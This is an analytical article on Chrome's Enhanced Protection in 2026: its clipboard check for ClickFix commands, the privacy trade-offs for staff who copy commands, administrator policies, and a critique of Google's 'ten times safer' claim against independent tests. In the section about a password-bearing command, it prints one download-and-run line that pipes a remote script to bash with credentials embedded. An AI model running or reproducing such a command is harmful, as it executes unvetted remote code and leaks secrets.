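Headlines in several countries suggested that Chrome would monitor what people copy. Miranda (2026), in *Google Chrome analizará lo que copias en el portapapeles para frenar estafas*, told Spanish readers that Google would start watching all the text they copy on their computers. Pplware's *Chrome vai começar a ler tudo o que copia* made a similar claim in Portuguese. In Greece, Amprazis (2026) wrote in the headline of *Ο Google Chrome θα ελέγχει πλέον τι κάνετε Copy-Paste* that Chrome would check what people copy and paste, for their own good. INTERNET Watch's *安全？ それともプライバシーの侵害？* (2026) asked whether the feature was safe or an invasion of privacy, and reported that the sending of clipboard data had caused controversy among some people.

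The articles were more precise than their headlines. Miranda explained that the check applies only under certain conditions, and Amprazis's summary mentions only suspicious commands.

When Enhanced Protection is on, Chrome checks text that someone copies from a web page in the browser. It doesn't check a paragraph copied in Word, so Miranda's headline is wrong about where the text comes from. Nothing in Google's description suggests that Chrome also checks what was already on the clipboard.

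The claim that Chrome reads what people copy is partly true. Chrome has to inspect text to find out whether it is a suspicious command, and most of what it inspects will be harmless. If someone copies a recipe from a small cooking blog, Chrome may compare the words with its list of download tools. This is a minor intrusion, because the browser already handles any text it copies, and Google doesn't receive the recipe.

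Pplware's article understates the scope of the check by saying it covers only sites that Chrome already considers suspicious. The pre-launch code exempted well-known sites and left the rest eligible.

IlSoftware.it came closest to describing the documented mechanism. It wrote that the feature does not check all copied text indiscriminately, but that the text Chrome selects can leave the device. The first claim is correct about what Chrome sends, but Chrome may inspect far more copied text than it sends.

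Gangwar is also right that the protection is more intrusive, since Chrome now sends Google two kinds of text that it used to keep on the device. Gangwar's claim that the protection is better is very likely true, but the size of the improvement is unknown without accuracy figures from Google.

### Is the trade acceptable?

TecnoAndroid called the arrangement an imperfect but reasonable compromise. It was writing about page text, for which Google's promises are strongest. The case for the arrangement as a whole depends on four claims: users chose this mode, Chrome sends only suspicious content, it removes identifying details first, and Google processes the content briefly.

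Users chose Enhanced Protection in the sense that it is off by default. Google told them in 2022 that it would keep adding protections as threats changed, and that new features would go through privacy reviews. But Google had counted more than a billion users by 2025, before Chrome had a copy check. They had agreed to share web addresses and samples of pages, and many would not have guessed that copied text would come next. Some may have relied on Google's argument in 2025 that checking pages on the device was better for privacy. Their agreement can reasonably cover improvements to existing checks, but Google should notify them before Chrome sends a new kind of data. Chrome could show a notice the first time it is about to send a copied command, with a button to turn off the copy check and keep the rest of the mode.

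The finished product probably does send Google only suspicious content, which greatly reduces the amount of data. But Chrome judges whether text is suspicious by what it looks like, and the commands for many legitimate installers look the same as harmful ones. Nobody outside Google can estimate how many harmless pages have text that the first screening flags as suspicious.

A report can still identify the user after Chrome removes identifying details from the command. Google describes hiding the IP address only for Standard Protection, and a signed-in user's report might be linked to their account. If Chrome deletes "Anna" from the text but sends the report under Anna's account, Google can still tell who copied the command. Removing the details still helps if someone later sees the text without the account information.

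Processing data only briefly would be the best safeguard, because nobody can steal or demand text that no longer exists. Google has promised this only for page text, and outsiders can't inspect its servers to confirm it. The promise still deserves some weight, since Google made it publicly and would risk legal trouble by breaking it. It doesn't cover verdicts, and Google presumably keeps at least some of those, since it otherwise couldn't add newly found scam sites to its lists.

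For most home users, the protection is worth the loss of privacy. Someone who never deliberately copies commands will send Google a command only when a web page puts one on the clipboard. On a ClickFix page, the attacker wrote that command, and it normally contains the attacker's server address and nothing about the victim. The privacy risk of the copy check is therefore almost entirely to people who copy legitimate commands, mainly developers and system administrators.

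### A command that contains a password

Suppose that Anna, an engineer, copies this line from her company's online documentation:

`curl -u anna:Maple-4471 https://build07.corp.example/setup.sh | bash`

It logs in to an internal server with a name and password, downloads a script and runs it. The pre-launch test would therefore mark it as suspicious. It is much less clear whether Chrome would remove the secrets before sending it.

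A good filter should catch "Anna", which is personal information. The password "Maple-4471" doesn't identify anyone, so Google's promise to remove personally identifiable information may not cover it, even though Chrome could recognise it as a password from its position after `-u`. Other commands contain secrets in less predictable places, such as a long access key inside a web address.

The server name is harder to deal with because it reveals something about the company's network, yet Safe Browsing needs the address in a command to judge whether the command is dangerous. If Chrome removed every address, Safe Browsing would lose the best evidence against real ClickFix commands. Chrome could remove only clearly internal addresses, but Google hasn't said that it does.

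In the pre-launch code, Chrome skipped pages on private networks, so if Anna copied from documentation on a server inside the office, that page would be exempt. The exemption might not apply if an outside provider hosts the company's documentation.

Such cases could add up at a large company. Suppose, as an invented example, that 500 engineers each copy two download-and-run commands from eligible pages every working day, or 250,000 a year. If 1 in 200 contains a password or key, that is 1,250 secrets. If a filter removed 90% of them, 125 would still reach Google.

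Few of those 125 would lead to any harm. A break-in through Google's security systems is unlikely, and the password to an internal server is of little use to someone who can't reach the server. A key to a cloud service is more serious because it may work from anywhere, and some companies' own rules would require them to replace it even if Google was the only outsider to receive it. The company would want to know how long Google keeps the command, but Google has made no specific promise about that.

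A password copied by itself, for example from a password manager's website, should be much safer because it contains no download tool or web address for Chrome's test to flag. One pre-launch version would still have reported the page to Google, but with less detail about the copied text.

### What organisations can switch off

Employers can choose the protection level for their staff. Google's 2022 post names a policy, SafeBrowsingProtectionLevel, that lets administrators turn on Enhanced Protection for the devices they manage. They can also do this in the Admin Console, Google's control panel for organisations. Because the policy sets the protection level, administrators can also use it to keep computers on Standard Protection. The argument that users opted in doesn't apply to staff whose employer made the choice.

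Clubic advises people with work computers to ask their IT department whether it allows Enhanced Protection. This is sensible for anyone who copies commands containing company secrets, because the department may not know that the mode now covers copied text.

Keeping a computer on Standard Protection stops both the copy check and the Gemini check, but it also removes the automatic deep scans of downloads and the milder site warnings. Reports of the October launch mention no policy for turning off the copy check alone. In the pre-launch code, however, Chrome skipped addresses that an employer had exempted. If the finished version does the same, a company could exempt its documentation site and leave Enhanced Protection on everywhere else. Commands copied from the company's own pages would then stay on the device, while ClickFix pages on other sites would still trigger the check.

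An organisation that can't exempt its own pages could use Standard Protection for the few teams whose commands contain passwords or keys, and Enhanced Protection for everyone else. Accountants and receptionists rarely copy commands, so the copy check would protect them with almost no loss of privacy. The engineering teams would then need other defences against ClickFix, such as security software that examines commands as they run. They could also keep passwords out of copied commands, which is safer regardless of what Chrome sends.

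## What "ten times safer" and "more than 1 billion users" measure

Google published its count of more than a billion Enhanced Protection users on 11 February 2025, for Safer Internet Day. Chrome had none of the Gemini checks then, and the three additions of 2026 came more than a year later. The count covers people who had turned the mode on by early 2025, not people who have received the new warnings. Rijo's headline about suspicious-site warnings "for 1 billion Enhanced Protection users" could give the impression that a billion people have received them, but the article dates the count to 2025 and notes that Google gave no newer one in October 2026.

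The number of people with the mode on may well have grown since, but the number with all three additions could still be smaller, because Google can switch features on for some users before others.

### How many people still have Standard Protection

Google's count would be more informative as a share of all Chrome users, but there is no reliable total to divide it by. Blaze Media's *Online threats are swamping the internet* (2026) gives an estimated total of 3.62 billion without naming a source, which would make a billion users about 28%. If the total were 3 billion, the share would be 33%, and if it were 4 billion, 25%, so between a quarter and a third is a reasonable guess.

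Google's figure of 5 billion devices is the wrong denominator because it includes everything Safe Browsing protects, even other companies' browsers, and a person with a phone and a laptop counts twice.

If Blaze Media's estimate is roughly right, more than 2.5 billion people use Chrome without Enhanced Protection. A few have turned Safe Browsing off, and nearly all the others must have Standard Protection, because it is the default. Standard Protection users probably include many people who have never opened Chrome's security settings and who may be less likely than most to recognise a fake virus alert. Google has not said whether it plans to extend the suspicious site warnings to them, according to Infobae's *Google lanza en Chrome alerta que distingue sitios "sospechosos"* (2026).

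### What Standard users gain indirectly

Standard users do benefit indirectly when Google adds scam sites found through Enhanced users to the shared lists, as Bawa and colleagues described in 2025. The benefit can be large when a scam site stays up for a long time. Suppose a fake shop is online for three weeks and 28% of its visitors have Enhanced Protection. There is about a 96% chance that at least one of the first ten visitors has it. If Chrome recognises the shop the first time an Enhanced user visits and Google lists it within the hour, nearly all later Standard visitors will get a warning.

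Many scam sites last long enough for a shared list to be useful, although Google's ten-minute figure for the average malicious site suggests that such sites are rare. *ReDence* (Kaur, Horáček and colleagues, 2026) followed 4,042 new scam sites for a week in October 2026, and about 59% were still reachable at the end, even though the researchers had reported all of them. The sample leaves out sites that disappeared before anyone could find them, so it can't refute Google's figure.

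Google has not said whether it also adds sites judged suspicious to the lists. That would be odd, because the lists trigger the red page, and Google created the milder pop-up for sites that don't warrant that page.

The sharing also affects any comparison between the modes. When Google finds a site through Enhanced users and lists it, Standard users also see warnings for it. Perfect sharing would make both groups safer and narrow the gap between them, so a small gap wouldn't prove that the new checks are useless.

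### From "phished less" to "ten times safer"

Google has compared the two modes at least four times since 2021, and it has changed both the measure and the list of threats.

| Date | Google's claim about Enhanced users | Measure | Risk compared with Standard, if the claim describes actual harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| June 2021 | "Successfully phished" 35% less than other users | People who fell for phishing | 65% |
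| December 2022 | Phished 20–35% less than Standard users | People who fell for phishing | 65–80% |
| February 2025 | Two times as safe from phishing and other scams | Not published | 50% |
| October 2026 | Ten times safer from phishing, social engineering, notification abuse and other scams | Average number of warnings shown | 10% |

The first claim, in Google's *New protections for Enhanced Safe Browsing users in Chrome* (2021), was about an outcome, the number of users phishers fooled. Google didn't explain how it counted them. It may have counted hijacked Google Accounts, or passwords that people typed into pages it later identified as phishing. The 2022 claim was of the same kind.

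Google gave no method for its 2025 "two times" claim. If that claim was also about people who fell for scams, it would be a moderate improvement on the 2022 figure. If it was already a count of warnings, the change from two to ten means the gap in warnings grew fivefold in 20 months. Either way, the four claims don't show that Enhanced Protection went from somewhat to vastly safer.

A footnote to Google's October post explains the basis for the "ten times" claim. Help Net Security and KultureGeek both report that Google compared the average number of safety warnings it showed to users of each mode. mobiFlip points out that this is not a count of attacks prevented.

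None of these reports makes clear which warnings Google counted. The claim covers notification abuse, in which a website gets permission to send notifications and uses it to push scams, so the count may include more than warnings about pages. It may also include the milder pop-up, which only Enhanced users see. Suppose that over several years a typical Standard user sees one red page and a typical Enhanced user sees three red pages and seven pop-ups. The Enhanced user then sees ten times as many warnings in total, but only three times as many red pages.

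### Do ten times as many warnings make people ten times safer?

More warnings can make people safer, but ten times as many warnings means a tenth of the harm only if the warnings are correct, people heed them, both groups encounter the same number of scams, and the number of scams without a warning falls to a tenth.

The last condition fails in most cases, even if everything else goes perfectly. Suppose a Standard user gets one warning and an Enhanced user gets ten. Google's ratio is the same however many scams each user meets, but the difference in safety changes. If each meets 20 scams, the Standard user meets 19 without a warning and the Enhanced user meets 10, so the Enhanced user is about twice as safe. If each meets 11, the numbers are 10 and 1, and the Enhanced user is ten times safer. If each meets 100, the numbers are 99 and 90, and the Enhanced user is only slightly safer.

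More generally, let *r* be the share of scams for which Standard Protection shows a warning. If Enhanced Protection shows ten times as many, and all of them are correct, then

times safer = (1 − *r*) ÷ (1 − 10*r*).

This equals ten only when *r* is one in eleven, or about 9%. And *r* can't be above 10%, because Enhanced Protection can't warn about more than 100% of scams. So if Google's ratio reflects only correct warnings and equal exposure, Standard Protection, Chrome's default setting, must miss at least nine scams in ten.

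Mistaken warnings raise Google's number without protecting anyone. A mode that put a warning on every hundredth page at random would look extremely safe by this measure. Google presumably doesn't do that, but the new pop-up is for less certain verdicts, so a higher share of its warnings will be wrong. People also ignore some correct warnings, as the studies of older browser warnings found. This table shows how much these failures affect the invented users, assuming that people who see no warning, or ignore one, fall for the scam.

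| Assumption | Scams that succeed out of 11, Standard / Enhanced | Times safer | Scams that succeed out of 20, Standard / Enhanced | Times safer |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All warnings are correct and people heed them | 10 / 1 | 10 | 19 / 10 | 1.9 |
| Two of the ten Enhanced warnings are mistaken | 10 / 3 | 3.3 | 19 / 12 | 1.6 |
| People ignore a quarter of the warnings | 10.25 / 3.5 | 2.9 | 19.25 / 12.5 | 1.5 |
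| Both | 10.25 / 5 | 2.1 | 19.25 / 14 | 1.4 |

Even in the most favourable case, two mistaken warnings out of ten reduce "ten times safer" to about three times.

Equal exposure is also doubtful, because people choose their mode. Someone who turns on extra protection may be unusually careful and meet few scams, or may have turned it on after a bad experience on the sort of site where scams are common. Google compared warnings per user, so people who browse more will also get more warnings. If the Enhanced user in the example meets 22 scams instead of 11 and gets ten warnings, 12 scams get no warning, compared with the Standard user's 10. The mode would still help that person, who would have met about 20 scams without a warning under Standard Protection, but its users would not be safer than the other group.

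The average can also rise tenfold while most people's protection stays about the same, if a small minority of users receive nearly all the additional warnings.

Some effects work in the other direction. If Chrome stops a website from sending scam notifications, the user never sees the dozens of scam pages those notifications would have opened. Chrome shows no warnings about those pages, so a count of warnings would understate the benefit. The lists that both modes share also narrow the gap. These effects could be large for some users, but nothing suggests that they cancel out the others.

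The absolute numbers are small. If Standard users get about one warning per device every four and a half years, which is the average for Safe Browsing as a whole, a tenfold difference means roughly nine more warnings per device in that time. That sounds less dramatic than "ten times safer", though one of those warnings could save someone's bank account.

### What independent tests have found

The best recent test is by Kaur and colleagues at Louisiana State University, because it used Chrome with Enhanced Protection on. From 1 to 28 October 2026, they watched a public feed of domains that had just received security certificates. Of 21.7 million domains, 552,809 had accessible websites. The researchers' AI system investigated these and flagged 4,054 as scams, and manual checks confirmed 4,042. As soon as the system found a scam, an automated copy of Chrome 150 began visiting it and continued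 until a warning appeared, for up to a week.

Chrome flagged 16.3% of the sites when they were discovered and 33.0% within seven days. The other products initially flagged a similarly low share.

| Protection | Flagged at discovery | Flagged within seven days |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome with Enhanced Protection | 16.3% | 33.0% |
| Microsoft SmartScreen (in Edge) | 15.2% | 31.3% |
| Malwarebytes Browser Guard | 16.0% | 38.4% |
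| Norton Safe Web | 20.1% | 46.1% |

The seven-day figures probably overstate detection, because the researchers immediately reported every site to all four services. Google confirmed that these reports had helped it identify 83 sites, equal to about an eighth of those that Chrome began to flag during the week, and the reports' full effect may be larger. In an earlier experiment, *PhishLang* (2024), reporting the missed pages helped raise Safe Browsing's detection of one evasive type of phishing from 35% to 73%.

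Chrome immediately flagged 44.1% of the sites that tried to steal login details, but only 7.9% of other scam sites, such as those of fake lenders and employers. Safe Browsing may not be meant to catch some of these. A fake roofing company's website can look like a real roofer's, and the fraud may consist of taking a deposit and never turning up.

Speed also varied. Among tech support scams, which Chrome's language-model check has covered since 2025, Chrome flagged 34.2% at discovery and 58.4% within a week. The median delay was 43 hours, apparently counting only the sites it flagged after discovery. For fake online shops, it was about 96 hours. A warning that arrives after two days can protect later visitors, but not those who came on the first day.

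The tech support result is the closest thing to an outside test of Gemini in Chrome, and it doesn't show an advantage. SmartScreen flagged 37.9% of the same 161 sites at discovery, and Norton flagged 38.5%. About two thirds of the sites also tried to steal login details, and all four products are relatively good at detecting sites that do this. Chrome's better score on tech support scams may therefore have little to do with Gemini.

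There are several reasons not to treat 16.3% as Enhanced Protection's recall for ordinary users. Every site counts equally, regardless of how many visitors it had. The researchers tested Chrome 150 in a month when Chrome 155 and 156 came out. It isn't clear whether their automated browser had the server-side Gemini check, or whether they counted the milder pop-up as a warning. Some scams ask for money only after several pages of questions, so a visit to the first page may give Chrome little to recognise. The feed also favours new domains, so the test provides little evidence about ClickFix pages on hacked websites.

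Older tests had similarly poor results. The British consumer group Which? tried 800 newly discovered phishing sites and found that Chrome blocked 28% of them on Windows and 25% on a Mac, while Firefox blocked 85% and 78%. Firefox also uses Safe Browsing, as *PhishLang* notes, so the lists alone can't easily explain such a gap. Differences in the browsers' settings or in how the testers ran them may have contributed.

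None of these tests compared Standard with Enhanced Protection, so they can't directly confirm or refute the tenfold ratio, but they make it hard to believe for phishing. Enhanced Protection can catch ten times as many phishing sites only if Standard Protection catches 10% or less. The 28% and 35% in the older tests are well above that limit, and both probably describe something close to the ordinary lists. The most likely explanation for the ratio is that most of the additional warnings concern things Standard Protection hardly covers, such as other kinds of scam, suspicious sites and notifications.

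If a tenfold ratio applied to the October results, Enhanced Protection would warn about 16.3% of scams and Standard about 1.6%, so Enhanced users would encounter 15% fewer scams without a warning than Standard users. For sites that steal login details, the warning rates would be 44.1% and 4.4%, and Enhanced users would encounter 42% fewer without a warning. These reductions are much closer to the claims Google made in 2021 and 2022 than to "ten times safer".

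### How Google could test the claim

The most convincing test would be a randomised trial. Google could recruit volunteers who have Standard Protection, turn on Enhanced Protection for half of them at random, and compare the two groups a year later. Random assignment would make the groups' browsing habits similar at the start. Google should measure harms (malware infections, hijacked accounts and money lost to scams) rather than warnings.

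Such harms are rare, but Google has enough users to measure them. Suppose 1 in 1,000 Standard users loses money to a web scam each year. To have an 80% chance of detecting a difference, the trial would need about 11,000 people in each group if Enhanced Protection cuts the risk to a tenth, 47,000 if it halves the risk, and 640,000 if it reduces the risk by 15%. The hardest part would be learning about losses, because many victims never report them. A survey could measure financial losses, and security scans could detect infections.

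A trial like this would miss the indirect benefit, since the Standard group would also get warnings about sites that Google discovers through Enhanced users. It would measure how much a person gains by turning on Enhanced mode, which "ten times safer" is supposed to describe.

Outside researchers could run a simpler test by opening the same new scam sites in two copies of Chrome, one in each mode, along with a few thousand legitimate sites to count false warnings. Kaur and colleagues already had most of the equipment for this. The test would measure each mode's recall, but not how many people each mode protects.

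Google may be able to make a similar comparison on real visits, because Chrome already repeats some Enhanced address checks with the Standard method. Google could count how often only one method finds a confirmed scam. Both methods would be checking the same pages, so differences in browsing habits would not affect the result. This would cover only the address checks, not Gemini or the copy check.

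In 2021, Google measured the share of users in each mode whom phishers fooled, so it evidently had a way to count them. It could also publish this measure for 2026.
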